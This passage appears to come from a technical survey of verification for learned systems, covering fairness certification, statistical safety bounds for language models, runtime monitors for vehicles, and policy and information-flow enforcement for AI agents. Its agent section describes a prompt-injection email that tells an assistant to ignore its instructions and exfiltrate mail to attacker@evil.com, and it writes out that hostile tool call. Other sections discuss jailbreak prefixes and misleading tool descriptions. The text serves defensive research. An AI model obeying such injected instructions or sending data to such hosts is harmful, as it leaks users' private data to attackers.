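*Quantifying Program Bias* (2017) describes FairSquare, a tool that can check whether a program hires qualified applicants from a minority at nearly the same rate as other qualified applicants. A solver finds boxes in the space of applicants, such as everyone aged 30 to 40 with five to ten years of experience, within which the program always gives the same decision. FairSquare adds up the probabilities of these boxes under the population model. The boxes of hired applicants give a lower bound on the hiring rate, and the boxes of rejected applicants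 give an upper bound. Each round adds boxes and tightens the bounds. Suppose the bounds place the hiring rate between 42% and 45% for the minority and between 48% and 50% for everyone else. The ratio of the two rates must then be between 0.84 and 0.94. If the specification requires a ratio of at least 0.8, the program is fair and FairSquare can stop.

FairSquare never gives a wrong answer, but it may run out of time. A later tool, VeriFair, instead samples applicants from the population model, so its answers have a small chance of being wrong. *Probabilistic Verification of Fairness Properties via Concentration* (2018) compares the two on FairSquare's own benchmark, with a limit of 900 seconds per problem. The paper notes that FairSquare's guarantee is stronger in theory, but its experiments set VeriFair's chance of error so low that it had essentially no effect on the answers. The results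 of both tools depend far more on the population model than on this difference in guarantees. If that model leaves out career breaks, neither tool can detect that the program penalises people who have had one.

### Seldonian algorithms

The *Seldonian algorithms* that Philip Thomas and colleagues presented in *Science* in 2019 build the statistical test into training. The user defines an undesirable behaviour and sets δ, the largest acceptable chance that the algorithm returns a model with that behaviour. The algorithm uses part of the data to choose a candidate model and the rest for a safety test. If the candidate fails, the algorithm reports that it found no solution.

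For example, a bank might require that a model wrongly reject at most 5% of creditworthy applicants, with δ = 0.05. If the candidate wrongly rejects 4 of 200 such applicants in the test data, the Clopper–Pearson upper bound is 4.5%, so the algorithm returns the model. If it wrongly rejects 2 of 100, the observed rate is still 2%, but the bound is 6.2%, so the algorithm returns no model. The stated confidence holds only if the test data play no part in choosing the candidate. It would no longer hold if the algorithm kept proposing candidates until one passed the test on the same data.

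Refusing to return a model is a sensible default when a bad model is worse than none, but it can happen often. *On Ensuring that Intelligent Machines Are Well-Behaved* (2017), an earlier version of the work, acknowledges that Seldonian algorithms such as its own method for non-discriminatory regression tend to need too much data to be practical. It focuses instead on "quasi-Seldonian" algorithms, which keep the chance of undesirable behaviour below δ only approximately, for instance by assuming that averages follow a bell curve. That assumption is often harmless for common errors but can be badly wrong for rare ones. If the test data contain no failures, the simplest bell-curve estimate puts the upper bound on the failure rate at zero, however few cases were tested.

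### Language models over a distribution of prompts

For a language model, D is a distribution over prompts, usually defined by a program that assembles them at random. A certifier draws prompts from D and runs the model. A judge, often another model, marks each response, and the certifier applies the Clopper–Pearson formula to the results. Chaudhary, Hu and colleagues (2025), in *Certifying Counterfactual Bias in LLMs*, used this approach to bound how often a model responds without bias to prompts that differ only in the demographic group they mention. They attached random prefixes to the prompts, including mixtures of known *jailbreaks*, texts designed to defeat a model's safety training.

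Wang, Chaudhary and colleagues (2025), in *How Catastrophic Is Your LLM?*, certified whole conversations. They arranged questions about chemical and biological weapons, cybercrime and other illegal activity in a network that linked similar questions. One distribution of conversations picks questions independently, and another follows a path of linked questions. A third moves towards a harmful target when the model answers and tends to move away when it refuses. For the worst model they tested, the probability of a catastrophic answer was at least 70%, with 95% confidence. Of the models tested, all from 2025 or earlier, Claude Sonnet 4 and Amazon's Nova Premier were the safest, and Mistral Large and DeepSeek-R1 had the highest risks.

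Agents choose among tools published by other people, some of whom may write misleading descriptions. In *Quantitative Certification of Agentic Tool Selection*, Yeon, Chaudhary and Singh (2025) tested an agent in which a search step shortlisted ten tools from a pool of 300 and a small language model chose one. In each of ten rounds, another language model added five misleading tools, with labels such as "[official]", and revised them based on the agent's last choice. After 1,000 trials, the researchers had 95% confidence that the agent would choose a suitable tool in all ten rounds at most about 20% of the time. This criterion is strict, since an agent with an independent 85% chance of choosing correctly in each round would also score about 20%. A single wrong choice can still be serious if the tool deletes files or exposes data.

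*Lumos* (Chaudhary, Jain and colleagues, 2025) introduces a programming language meant to make such distributions easier to write and inspect. One example program generates driving scenes for Qwen-VL, a model that takes images and text. The model's responses were safe at most 10% of the time in right turns in the rain.

Sampling responses works poorly when the harm is rare. In *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models*, Nazeri, Schmuck and colleagues (2026) give an example where no sampled response to a prompt was harmful, so the lower bound on the probability of harm was zero. They instead search for harmful responses and add up the probabilities the model assigns to those responses. The total is always a lower bound, however they find the responses.

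In *BEAVER*, Wadhwa, Suresh and colleagues (2025) compute lower and upper bounds on the probability of an acceptable response. Their tool repeatedly extends the most probable unfinished response and checks each response once it is complete. Suppose the acceptable responses found so far have a total probability of 62%, the unacceptable ones 25%, and the unfinished ones 13%. The probability of an acceptable response must then be between 62% and 75%. Wadhwa and colleagues call a prompt risky if this probability is below 90%, so this prompt is risky however the unfinished responses end.

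They checked 300 random prompts for each of three tasks on five open models with 4 to 70 billion parameters. Each prompt combined a request with an adversarial instruction. In the privacy task, for every model, at least 42% of prompts were risky, meaning they had more than a 10% chance of producing a real email address from a leaked collection. In the toxicity task, at least 83% were risky for three models, but for two newer models the lower bounds were only 14% and 26%. These percentages hold with 95% confidence because the prompts are a sample, but the bounds for each prompt are exact.

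For toxicity, the method identified up to 7.6 times as many risky prompts as sampling responses did. It took about two minutes per prompt for responses of at most 32 tokens. The number of possible responses grows exponentially with length, so page-long answers are probably far beyond what the method can handle. It also needs the model's token probabilities, which companies often do not reveal.

Each of these certificates depends on its judge. *Tight PAC-Bayes Generalisation Guarantees for Large Language Model Judges* (2026) gives a bound on the judge's errors. But this bound also assumes that the prompts and responses in use come from the same distribution as the test sample, so developers have to recompute it whenever that distribution changes.

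### Repeated attempts by an agent

Developers also use test results to argue that an agent is unable to do something dangerous. One method divides a task into ordered milestones and runs the agent a few times from a prepared state before each one. In *Clean Sheets and Checkpoints*, Yanambaka Venkata, McBride and colleagues (2026) examined what can be concluded when every run fails. They took a published record in which two early Gemini models failed all ten runs at each of four milestones, and asked how many attempts an agent could make before its chance of completing the task might exceed 1%.

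At 97.5% confidence, the 40 failures are compatible with a success rate of about 8.8% at every milestone. If each failure sends the agent back to the start, it needs four successes in a row, with a probability of 0.088⁴, or about 0.00006. The 40 failures then support a guarantee for 169 attempts, counting each try at a milestone as one attempt. If the agent keeps its progress after a failure, any four successes are enough, and the guarantee extends to only 10 attempts.

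Even these figures assume that the success rates in the tests are upper limits in deployment, whatever has happened to the agent so far. The tests can't check this. Suppose that in 10% of deployments the agent finds a leaked password and succeeds at everything, and in the rest it always fails. Each milestone, tested separately, has a success rate of 10%. The probability of two in a row is also 10%, but multiplying the two rates gives 1%.

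### Attackers who choose their inputs

Suppose a chatbot gives safe answers to three million random prompts from the distribution D. Then, with 95% confidence, at most one in a million prompts from D gets an unsafe answer. That may be acceptable for ordinary users, although a service that answers a billion prompts a day could still give 1,000 of them unsafe answers.

A bound on the average failure rate under D does not limit how often an attacker succeeds, because attackers choose their prompts instead of drawing them from D. Anyone who finds one prompt that causes a failure can send it every time and share it with others. There may also be many such prompts. If D were uniform over the roughly 10⁴⁷ sequences of ten tokens, a failure rate of one in a million would mean 10⁴¹ failing prompts. Chaudhary, Hu and colleagues therefore describe their specifications as average-case, even though their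 prefixes include jailbreaks.

*Risk-certified prompt optimization for LLM-as-a-judge guardrails* (2026) bounds the share of attacks that a guardrail misses, assuming that the attacks are independent draws from a fixed distribution. Even if the tests use real attacks, deploying the guardrail changes that distribution, because attackers whom it blocks will try something else. The adaptive tests that Wang and Yeon and their colleagues designed come closer to a real attacker, but they cover only adaptation by a rule that the researchers chose in advance.

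Lower bounds on risk are more useful when there are attackers. If random conversations from D produce a catastrophic answer at least 70% of the time, an attacker can succeed at least that often by drawing from D. A certificate that a model is dangerous therefore remains valid, provided the judge is right, but a certificate that it is safe does not. Most published bounds for language models are lower bounds on risk.

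A safety guarantee against attackers would have to cover the worst prompt in some set, as randomised smoothing covers the worst change within its radius. Wadhwa and colleagues cite methods that provide such guarantees for limited changes to a prompt's tokens or to their numerical representation. A request that an attacker has completely rewritten falls outside these sets, and no one has defined a set that includes every rewording and is small enough for a useful proof.

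## From a verified component to a safe system

Suppose engineers have shown that a pedestrian detector fails on at most 0.0001 of the images in D. A camera that takes 10 images a second produces 36,000 an hour, so the bound allows an expected 3.6 failures per hour of driving. Lowering the bound to one failure in a million hours is not realistic. The rate per image would have to be about one in 36 billion, and confirming that by testing would take more than 100 billion images without a failure.

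Most single failures do no harm, because the next image arrives a tenth of a second later. The danger comes from failures in a row, which a bound on the average rate does not limit. A detector that misses people in dark clothing will miss the same person in successive images. If failures were independent, the chance of missing a pedestrian in 20 successive images would be 10⁻⁸⁰. When they are not, an average of 3.6 failures an hour is compatible with one run of 50 missed images every 14 hours. Such a run lasts five seconds, in which a car at 50 km/h covers about 70 metres.

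The car's actions also affect which images the detector receives next. A small steering error points the camera towards the kerb, so the next image looks less like the training data and the next error may be larger. The images can therefore drift away from D even if D described the road correctly.

Zheng, Ruchkin and colleagues argue in *Assuring Learning-Enabled Cyber-Physical Systems with Foundation Models* (2026) that a proved property of a model is useful in practice only when someone connects it to the requirements of the whole system. Engineers can try to make that connection with contracts between components, analysis of the whole control loop, a search for failures in simulation, or a verified fallback that takes over while the system runs.

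### Contracts between components

An *assume-guarantee contract* states what a component may assume and what it must guarantee in return. For a car that has to stay 2 metres from every obstacle, the contracts might be:

| Component | Assumes | Guarantees |
|---|---|---|
| Detector | Daylight, speed of at most 50 km/h | Reports every obstacle before it is closer than 35 m |
| Controller | A report at 35 m or more | Commands full braking within 0.2 seconds |
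| Brakes | Dry road, speed of at most 50 km/h | Stop the car within 30 m of the command |

The car travels 2.8 m before the command and at most 30 m after it, so it stops at least 2.2 m from the obstacle. Each assumption has to follow from another component's guarantee or from the environment model E. Engineers can then replace the brakes and recheck only one row.

Contracts may depend on each other in a circle. For example, the detector needs a speed of at most 50 km/h to avoid blurred images, and the software that limits the speed may need the detector to read road signs. The argument is still sound if each guarantee relies only on the others having held at earlier moments, because the proof can then proceed step by step from the start of the drive.

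The detector's contract is the difficult one, because nobody has a formula for "obstacle" in terms of pixels. *Compositional Verification for Autonomous Systems with Deep Learning Components* (2018), an early proposal for such contracts, therefore describes the evidence they provide as conditional. *Assumption Generation for the Verification of Learning-Enabled Autonomous Systems* (2023) instead analyses the system without the network and the sensors, and derives which sequences of predictions would keep the system safe. The result is an exact specification for the network, which engineers can also use to monitor its outputs.

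A contract does not help much if the network sometimes violates it, so Watson, Alur and colleagues (2025) used the network's error rates in *Scenario-based Compositional Verification of Autonomous Systems with Neural Perception*. They studied TaxiNet, an experimental Boeing network that uses camera images to estimate an aircraft's distance from the taxiway centre line and the direction it points. For each position of the aircraft, they counted how often the network gave each estimate. They combined these frequencies with models of the controller and the aircraft's motion to compute the probability that the aircraft would stray too far from the line.

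TaxiNet estimated the heading correctly in 91% of bright images and 54% of dark ones. Over two stretches of 20 time steps each, the worst-case probability of straying was 3% if both were bright and 55% if both were dark. Both figures assume at least a 90% chance that the aircraft starts on the line and points along it. Pooling all the images gave 31%, which is far too high for day and far too low for night.

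Bounds for separate stretches combine as the per-step errors of a world model do, so ten stretches at 3% each give 1 − 0.97¹⁰, or 26%. This calculation holds only if the aircraft's possible positions at the end of each stretch satisfy the next bound's assumptions about its starting position. The model also draws the estimate at each step independently of earlier mistakes, so it would underestimate the risk if one patch of glare misled the network for several seconds.

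### Properties that do not split

Stopping distances and time limits are easy to divide among components because their shares add up to the total. Other properties of a system do not follow from the properties of its parts taken separately.

Contracts that limit each component's failure rate separately don't determine how often two components fail together. If a camera and a laser scanner each miss one obstacle in 10,000, both miss the same one only once in 100 million cases if their failures are independent, but once in 10,000 if their misses always coincide, for example because fog blinds both. *GURU* (2026), a paper on automating critical engineering work, notes that in the digital controls of nuclear plants, the main concern about such joint failures is a software fault shared by every identical copy. The usual defence is to build the copies differently.

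A system can also fail to make progress. If two robots meet at a doorway and each follows the rule "let the other go first", neither will ever move.

A system can also be unfair or leak a secret even when each component passes its own check. Suppose two stages of a hiring process each pass half of the men and half of the women. If the same men pass both stages but no woman does, the process accepts half of the men and none of the women. For secrecy, suppose one program publishes a random number and another publishes the sum of that number and a secret. Either output alone reveals nothing about the secret, but subtracting one from the other gives it. Fairness and secrecy are *hyperproperties*, which concern a whole set of runs rather than one run at a time. Seshia (2021) uses this distinction in *Formal Specification for Machine Learning Systems* to classify specifications for learned systems.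 Verifying any such property requires analysing the components together.

### Reachability of the closed loop

*Reachability analysis* starts from a set of possible states, such as every position and speed the car might have, and computes a set that contains every state the system could be in one step later. Repeating this gives the states reachable over a period of time. If none of them is unsafe, the system is safe for that period in the model.

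Suppose a car is at most 1 m to either side of the lane's centre. At each step, a network steers it halfway back to the centre, with a proven error of at most 0.1 m. The new offset is at most 0.5 × 1 + 0.1 = 0.6 m, then 0.4 m, then 0.3 m, so the car never leaves the lane. But if the verifier doesn't track how the correction depends on the offset, it must include the case of a car 1 m to the left that steers 0.6 m further left. The bound then grows to 1.6 m after one step and 2.5 m after two. Most of the work in these methods goes into tracking such dependencies over many steps.

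*Case Study* (Ivanov, Carpenter and colleagues, 2019) applied this analysis to the F1/10, a small autonomous racing car. The car drives at up to about 2.4 m/s through hallways with right-angled turns. Its only sensor is LiDAR, which measures the distance to the nearest surface along 1,081 laser rays. A network turns some of these distances into a steering command. The property was that, from any starting position in a range 20 cm wide, the car never comes within 0.3 m of a wall for seven seconds, which is long enough to take one turn.

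They trained networks with two hidden layers of 64 or 128 neurons by reinforcement learning, in which a program learns by trial and error from rewards. The tool Verisig rewrote each network as equations of the same kind as those for the car's motion, so that an existing reachability tool could analyse both together. To keep the bounds tight, they divided the starting range into 40 or more pieces, each of which took an hour or more on average. Verisig verified seven of the 12 networks that used 21 rays. It nearly finished verifying one of the two networks that used 41 rays, and finished neither of the two that used 61.

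Analyzing the network took only about 10% of the computing time. Most of the rest went to modeling the car and its sensor, because a ray near a corner may hit either of two walls and the tool has to follow both cases. A faster network verifier would have saved little time.

Ivanov and colleagues then drove the real car ten times with each of the 12 networks, in a hallway with the same dimensions as the modeled one. With most reflective surfaces covered, about 90% of the runs were safe. With the surfaces uncovered, one verified network had no safe runs out of ten and another had only two. A laser ray that bounces off a shiny surface may never return to the sensor, and the car then receives the same reading as for open space. E did not include these reflections, so the proof, though correct, did not cover them.

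In the covered hallway, the seven verified networks were safe in 64 of 70 runs (91%) and the other five in 45 of 50 (90%). These results do not really support Ivanov and colleagues' conclusion that verification was strongly correlated with safe driving when the hallway resembled the model.

Cameras are harder to model than lasers because no short formula can predict the image a camera will produce. *Stochastic World Models for Verifying Vision-Based Neural Feedback Systems* (Akinwande, Kochenderfer and Barrett, 2026) replaces the camera with a small network that generates images from the car's distance and speed and from conditions such as the lighting. The verifier must show that the car stops before a stationary obstacle for every image this network can generate. Because the conditions may change arbitrarily from one image to the next, the proof also covers long runs of bad images.

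They divided the possible starts into 10,000 cells. For an older greyscale image generator, an earlier method had left 3,868 cells undecided. The new method decided every cell in 1,043 hours on a graphics processor, proving 6,536 safe and finding a crash in each of the other 3,464. However, that generator reproduces a scene's average brightness and loses its structure. With a more faithful colour model, Akinwande and colleagues proved 4,677 cells safe and found crashes in 3,498 after 550 hours. Nearly all of the remaining 1,825 were still unanalysed, and the researchers expect the complete job to take about 3,600 hours.

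The images are only 32 pixels wide, and both models imitate a simulator rather than a real camera. Akinwande and colleagues acknowledge that no formal guarantee connects the two. For the colour images, they also had to replace the benchmark's attention-based perception network with one that is easier to verify. With a limit of about 10 hours for each network, they verified 120 cells with the easier one and 10 with one of the original type and size, although the original type measured distances more than twice as accurately.

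### Searching for failures in simulation

When a system is too complex for a proof, engineers can search for a counterexample. Dreossi, Donzé and Seshia did this for an emergency-braking system in *Compositional Falsification of Cyber-Physical Systems with Machine Learning Components* (2017). The property they tested was that the car never hits a stationary vehicle ahead. Radar measures distances up to 30 m, and beyond that the car relies on a neural network to decide whether a camera image shows a vehicle.

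Dreossi and colleagues first left the images out of the search because there are far too many to cover. They simulated the car from many starting speeds and distances, once with an imaginary classifier that is always right and once with one that is always wrong. If both versions avoid a crash, or both crash, the real network is unlikely to affect the outcome. The search can then concentrate on the starting conditions where only the perfect classifier avoids a crash.

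For those starts, they generated road images that varied in brightness and in the other vehicle's distance and sideways position. The image classifier AlexNet tended to miss vehicles in the middle of the road in dim pictures. When the car started at 25 mph and 40 m away, such an error led to a crash. When it started at 28 mph and 50 m away, it avoided a crash despite the error. Another classifier, Inception-v3, missed a vehicle less than 5 m away, but this made no difference because the car relied on radar at that distance. A test of the classifier alone would have counted all these errors equally.

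A classifier that is sometimes right could do more harm than one that is always wrong, for example if each new detection restarts a timer in the braking software. The method therefore helps direct the search but does not prove that the other starts are safe. Dreossi and colleagues say that one cannot expect to prove such systems correct, though they hope to extend the approach to verification.

Two later tools make such searches easier to set up. Scenic is a programming language for describing distributions of scenes, such as a car parked badly at the side of a road. VerifAI draws scenes from a Scenic program, runs them in a simulator and looks for ones that reduce the margin by which the system satisfies a signal temporal logic formula. *Verified Artificial Intelligence and Autonomy* (Seshia, 2021) describes an example in which a car had to change lanes within 15 m of an accident, and its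 perception network reported an obstacle 30 m away as 14.5 m away.

Seshia also reports a test of how well such findings carry over to a real car. The scenario was a right turn with a pedestrian crossing the road. Of 1,294 simulations, 2% violated the safety property. The team repeated seven selected cases on a test track with a real car and a robotic target. Cases that were unsafe in simulation were unsafe on the track 62.5% of the time, and safe cases were safe 93.5% of the time. The car's software lost track of the pedestrian several times. Seven cases are too few for precise rates, but they show that simulation can find real faults and can also miss some.

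A search that finds no failures does not prove that there are none. The 3/n bound does not apply either, because the tool chooses each scene based on earlier ones. To get a statistical bound, engineers have to run a separate test with random scenes, and that bound will hold for the simulator.

### Runtime assurance

The remaining approach is to keep the system safe even when the learned component fails. The standard design is the *Simplex architecture*, which Lui Sha described in 2001. As *The Use of the Simplex Architecture to Enhance Safety* (2025) explains, it combines an untrusted high-performance controller, a simple safe controller, and a monitor that selects which one controls the system. SOTER, a programming framework for robots, follows the same design.

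Bansal, Yeghiazaryan and colleagues (2026), in *Synergistic Simplex*, set out what engineers have to establish for such a design to be safe:

- The monitor's check is sound, so any action it approves really is safe.
- The system starts in a set of states from which the safe controller always has a safe action, and that action leads to another state in the set.
- The conditions under which engineers proved all this, such as working brakes, still hold.

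The second condition determines when to switch. Suppose a car travels at 10 m/s, brakes at 5 m/s² and must stop 2 m from an obstacle. It needs 10²/(2 × 5) = 10 m to stop, so it must start braking by the time the obstacle is 12 m away. But if the monitor checks only every 0.1 seconds, the learned controller could accelerate between checks. At 3 m/s², the car would get about 1 m closer and reach 10.3 m/s, from which it needs 10.6 m to stop. The monitor must therefore intervene when the obstacle is 2 + 1 + 10.6 = 13.6 m away. Delays and errors in the distance measurement increase this threshold. Returning control to the learned controller requires a stricter threshold, or the car may alternate between braking and accelerating.

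A *shield* works on single actions. Before the system runs, a program computes the states from which the system can obey a rule forever, whatever the environment does. The shield then blocks or replaces any action that would take the system out of this set. In shielded reinforcement learning, it can also do this during training, so a robot can learn to avoid stairs without falling down them. *Semantic Quorum Assurance* (2026) adapts the idea to changes that AI agents propose to cloud infrastructure, but its judgement of what is safe is only probabilistic.

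This approach requires a monitor that can detect danger, but no proof about the learned controller, which can be of any size. In Bansal and colleagues' design, the monitor uses LiDAR and a geometric algorithm with no learned parts. The algorithm provably detects any obstacle that is tall enough for its distance, and this detection limit restricts how fast the car may drive. The proof assumes that the sensors work and that obstacles stand still or move away, so it does not cover a pedestrian who steps into the road.

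In simulation, they made the learned driving system overlook an obstacle, with ten runs for each combination:

| Design | Obstacle in the car's lane: runs with a collision | Obstacle in the next lane: routes completed |
|---|---|---|
| Learned system alone | 10 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| With the monitor | 0 of 10 | 1 of 10 |
| With a monitor that also uses lane positions | 0 of 10 | 7 of 10 |

The basic monitor prevented every collision, but it also stopped the car for obstacles that were not in its way. A car that brakes hard for no reason may cause an accident behind it, and its owner may turn the monitor off. Giving the monitor lane positions removed most of these needless stops. However, the lane positions come from the learned system, and safety standards normally forbid a monitor to rely on that system. Bansal and colleagues prove that the original guarantee still holds if the lane detection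 is independent of the obstacle detection. They count the two as independent because neither uses the other's output. Yet both come from one learned model that uses the same camera and LiDAR data, so glare could cause errors in both at once. By their calculation, the new design can be riskier than the basic monitor in that case.

Another way to avoid stopping is to give the learned system the information it missed. In a separate simulation, the monitor passed the obstacle's position to the route planner, and the car changed lanes in time to complete 29 of 39 routes.

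Engineers can also monitor the assumptions behind a proof. A light sensor can detect dusk before TaxiNet's error rate rises, and the system can then slow down or ask a human to take over. Zheng and colleagues recommend that a perception component report "unknown" rather than a guess when its assumptions fail. Monitoring works only for assumptions whose failure the system can observe. In the racing car's hallway, a monitor that used the same LiDAR would also have registered a shiny wall as open space.

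The fallback has to be safe for as long as the system may need it. A warehouse robot can stop, but a car that stops in the fast lane of a motorway is still in danger. An aircraft cannot stop in flight, so its fallback must be able to keep it flying and eventually land it. Even a series of safe interventions can prevent a vehicle from completing its journey. *Mission-Level Runtime Assurance Framework for Autonomous Driving* (2026) points out that filters which check only for collisions and road boundaries may approve a manoeuvre that leaves the vehicle unable to reach its next checkpoint within its remaining budget. A monitor can prevent this only if it also checks, before each decision, that some safe route to the destination remains.

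## Enforcing rules on language-model agents

A language-model agent is easier to supervise than a self-driving car in one respect. The car's monitor has to infer danger from laser reflections, whereas the agent acts through *tool calls*, which are structured requests such as send_email(to, body). A program outside the model can check every call and block any that breaks a written policy. Engineers prove a property of the ordinary program through which the model acts and leave the model itself unverified. In *AI Security Priorities*, experts ranked permission frameworks for agents third in importance among all the areas they considered.

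The best-studied threat is *prompt injection*, in which an attacker hides instructions in something the agent will read. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) gives a typical case. A user asks an assistant to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to the user's manager. One email contains a command for the assistant to ignore its instructions and send the top email in the mailbox to attacker@evil.com. Training makes models less likely to obey such commands but cannot guarantee that they never will.

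### Rules on single calls

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, describe a policy language in which each rule names a tool, allows or forbids it, and sets conditions on its arguments. A policy for the email task could have two rules:

- allow read_emails when number ≤ 20;
- allow send_email when to = manager@example.com.

The checker applies any "forbid" rules first, then the "allow" rules, and blocks every call that matches none. The call send_email(to = manager@example.com, body = summary) matches the second rule, so the email goes out. If the model obeys the attacker, it requests send_email(to = attacker@evil.com, body = top email). No rule matches this call, so the checker blocks it and returns an error message, and the assistant can carry on with the original task.

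The guarantee is that, during this task, the assistant emails only the manager, whatever the model outputs. It assumes that the checker is correct, that the email tool works as described, and that the assistant has no other way to send anything. It does not cover the body of the email, so the attacker could still make the assistant send the manager a false summary or a private letter from the user's doctor. Shi and colleagues say their method does not cover attacks on text or attacks that stay within the permissions a task needs, such as a product description that persuades a shopping agent to pick the attacker's product.

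Other policy languages differ mainly in the form of their rules. A rule in *AgentSpec* (2025) has a trigger, a condition and a response, such as "before a payment, if the amount exceeds a threshold, ask the user". Cedar, which Amazon developed for access control in ordinary software, also uses rules that permit or forbid actions.

Because the rules have an exact meaning, a solver can check a policy before any agent runs. Engineers can find gaps by having the solver search for a call that the policy allows but a company-wide rule prohibits, such as an email to an outside address. They can also find contradictions by searching for "allow" rules that never take effect because "forbid" rules cover them completely.

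Progent uses a solver to determine which changes to an agent's policy need approval. Nobody can write a policy by hand for every request, so a language model drafts one from the user's words and proposes changes as the agent learns more. The solver checks whether the new policy would allow any call that the old one blocked. If so, the change needs approval. Other changes, such as narrowing "message anyone" to "message only Alice", take effect automatically. Only 6% of changes needed approval on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, banking, travel and messaging tasks.

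With GPT-4o as the agent, Progent cut the success rate of attacks on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%, even though every expansion of the policy was approved in the experiment. When a person reviewed the first policy and each expansion, no attack succeeded. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that malicious text in a tool's output may lead the model to loosen the policy. The solver will detect the loosening, but someone still has to refuse it. The solver also can't detect that the first policy was already too broad, because it compares policies with each other and not with what the user wanted.

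### How far simple rules go

*Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety* (Hong, She and colleagues, 2026) examined 126 requirements for three agents, which handled airline bookings, a car's voice commands and medical records. Ordinary code could enforce 93 of the requirements (74%), and 88 of those needed only simple checks, such as confirming that a ticket belongs to the customer before cancelling it. The airline benchmark stated the rule against cancelling a flight that has already flown only in the model's instructions, so an agent could break it.

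Without the checks, the agents broke enforceable rules in 20% to 78% of tasks, even though their instructions contained the full policy. The checks prevent all such violations by construction, and they did not make the agents less useful. The car assistant's task completion rate rose from 59% to 72%, while the rate for the airline agent with GPT-5 rose from 68% to 70%, which is not statistically significant. Hong and colleagues suggest that a refusal with a clear error message lets the agent try again instead of finishing with the wrong result.

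The remaining requirements concerned tone, invented facts, the order of a conversation, or judgement. One was "Do not proactively offer compensation unless the user explicitly asks for it". Engineers could replace it with a rule that a program can check, by blocking the compensation tool until the customer types "compensation", but the tool would then stay blocked for a customer who asks for "money back".

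All three agents have narrow jobs, and language models wrote the policy for the medical one. The results may not apply to general-purpose assistants, for which few people have written checkable rules. Hong and colleagues reviewed 80 benchmarks for agent safety and security and found that 68 contained no requirement precise enough to verify.

### Tracking where data came from

A list of approved recipients works only if someone knows the recipients in advance. *Information-flow control* instead attaches labels to data and checks them before each action. In FIDES, a system by Costa and colleagues, a label records whether the data is trusted and who may read it. Data derived from several sources gets the strictest combination of their labels. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read a file, and Ben, Carla and Dev may read an email, only Ben and Carla may read a summary of both, and the summary is untrusted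 if either source is.

Applied directly, this would make an email assistant useless. Once the model has read an untrusted email, everything it produces counts as untrusted, including its decision to send the summary. FIDES and CaMeL, a 2025 design from Google DeepMind, solve this by using two models. A planner sees the user's request and chooses the tool calls. A quarantined model reads the emails but has no tools. The planner refers to the emails only by a variable name, so their text never reaches it. The email task then takes three steps:

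1. read_emails(3), with the result stored as E;
2. ask the quarantined model to summarise E, with the result stored as S;
3. send_email(to = manager, body = S).

Suppose the rule requires both the decision to send and the recipient to be trusted. The checker allows step 3 because both come from the user's request. If the quarantined model follows the attacker's instructions, it can only write the attacker's words into S, where they become part of the summary. A call that takes its recipient from E or S fails the check because the address has an untrusted label.

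The rule therefore guarantees that text from an untrusted message cannot cause an email to be sent or determine who receives it. It also blocks some harmless requests. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a plan that finds Bob's address in a channel's messages and emails him about a meeting. The rule blocks this plan because the checker cannot distinguish Bob's real address from one that an attacker planted.

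A second rule can protect secrets by requiring that every recipient be allowed to read the body. The manager could then receive the summary only if allowed to read all three emails. Costa and colleagues prove that such rules stop secret data from being passed on directly, but information can still leak through the agent's choices. If an agent posts a public notice only when a confidential file mentions a merger, anyone who sees the notice learns about the merger. Preventing this kind of leak would mean banning almost every public action after the agent has read anything confidential.

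When a task depends on what an email says, FIDES can show the planner a restricted answer, such as yes or no to "Does this email request a meeting?" An attacker can make the answer wrong but cannot fit an instruction into it.

According to *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026), these designs assume that the user, the planner's model and the tools are trustworthy. The fixed list of recipients did not require trusting the model. A planner that tried to leak a file could satisfy the first rule, because its own decisions count as trusted. The rule about readers would stop it from sending the file to anyone outside the permitted group, if the labels are correct and the policy makes no exception for trusted decisions.

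Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) show in *Can CaMeLs Talk?* that the guarantee can also fail when one protected agent passes untrusted data to another that treats it as an instruction. Their remedy sends data and instructions through separate channels. It reduces the number of tasks completed, but this reduction tends to be smaller for more capable models.

### What enforcement costs

Early versions reduced the number of tasks agents completed. With GPT-4o, FIDES stopped every attack in AgentDojo but completed only 41% to 59% of the tasks in each of four settings, compared with 70% to 99% for an unprotected agent. With OpenAI's o1, which was better at working with variables, FIDES completed 68% of travel tasks, up from 41%.

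*Flowsh* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) reports the newest measurements, made with GPT-6.2 Sol. It applies information-flow control to the shell, the command line through which agents run programs. A checker often cannot predict what a command will do, because the command may start other programs. Flowsh therefore runs each command in isolation and records which files and websites the command reads. It holds back changes to files until the command ends, then applies those that the policy allows. It checks network requests before they leave, because they cannot be undone once sent.

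Kim and colleagues ran 17 office tasks three times each under five levels of protection. In one setting, the agent asked for approval whenever the defence could not guarantee that an action was safe, and an ideal approver refused only the actions that an attack had influenced. In the other, no approver was available. They assumed a worst-case attack, in which the attacker controls everything the model outputs after it reads the malicious text.

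| Protection | Tasks completed with an approver | Requests per completed task | Tasks completed without an approver | Successful attacks without an approver |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Almost no restrictions | 96% | 6.7 | 94% | 100% |
| Standard limits on files and websites | 76% | 5.7 | 76% | 8% |
| Strict limits | 47% | 0 | 47% | 0% |
| Labels for the agent, but not for each command | 61% | 1.8 | 35% | 0% |
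| Flowsh | 88% | 1.2 | 59% | 0% |

Without an approver, Flowsh completed only 6 of 27 runs on tasks that combined untrusted and confidential data, but all 24 of the other runs. This is expected under the policy, because an agent that has read both a stranger's web page and a private file could leak the file. On Terminal-Bench, a set of 89 programming and system tasks, Flowsh completed 62% without an approver, compared with 78% for an almost unrestricted agent.

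Flowsh also made completed tasks take 17% to 34% longer and use 17% to 55% more tokens. A single command took 0.4 to 1 second, up from less than 0.1 seconds.

Kim and colleagues cite Anthropic's report that users approve about 93% of the permission requests from its coding agent, Claude Code, and pay less attention as the requests accumulate. The high approval rate could mean that most requests are harmless, but the declining attention is a danger. Fewer requests should help. In 39 of 45 attacks, Flowsh's first request was about the attack itself, so the approver would not have already approved a series of harmless ones. Kim and colleagues have not tested whether people make better decisions when they get fewer requests.

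### Rules over a whole plan

A series of steps can cause harm even if each one is allowed. If payments above $1,000 need confirmation, an agent can still make ten payments of $900 without it. To prevent this, a policy has to restrict the whole sequence, for example by limiting the total paid per day.

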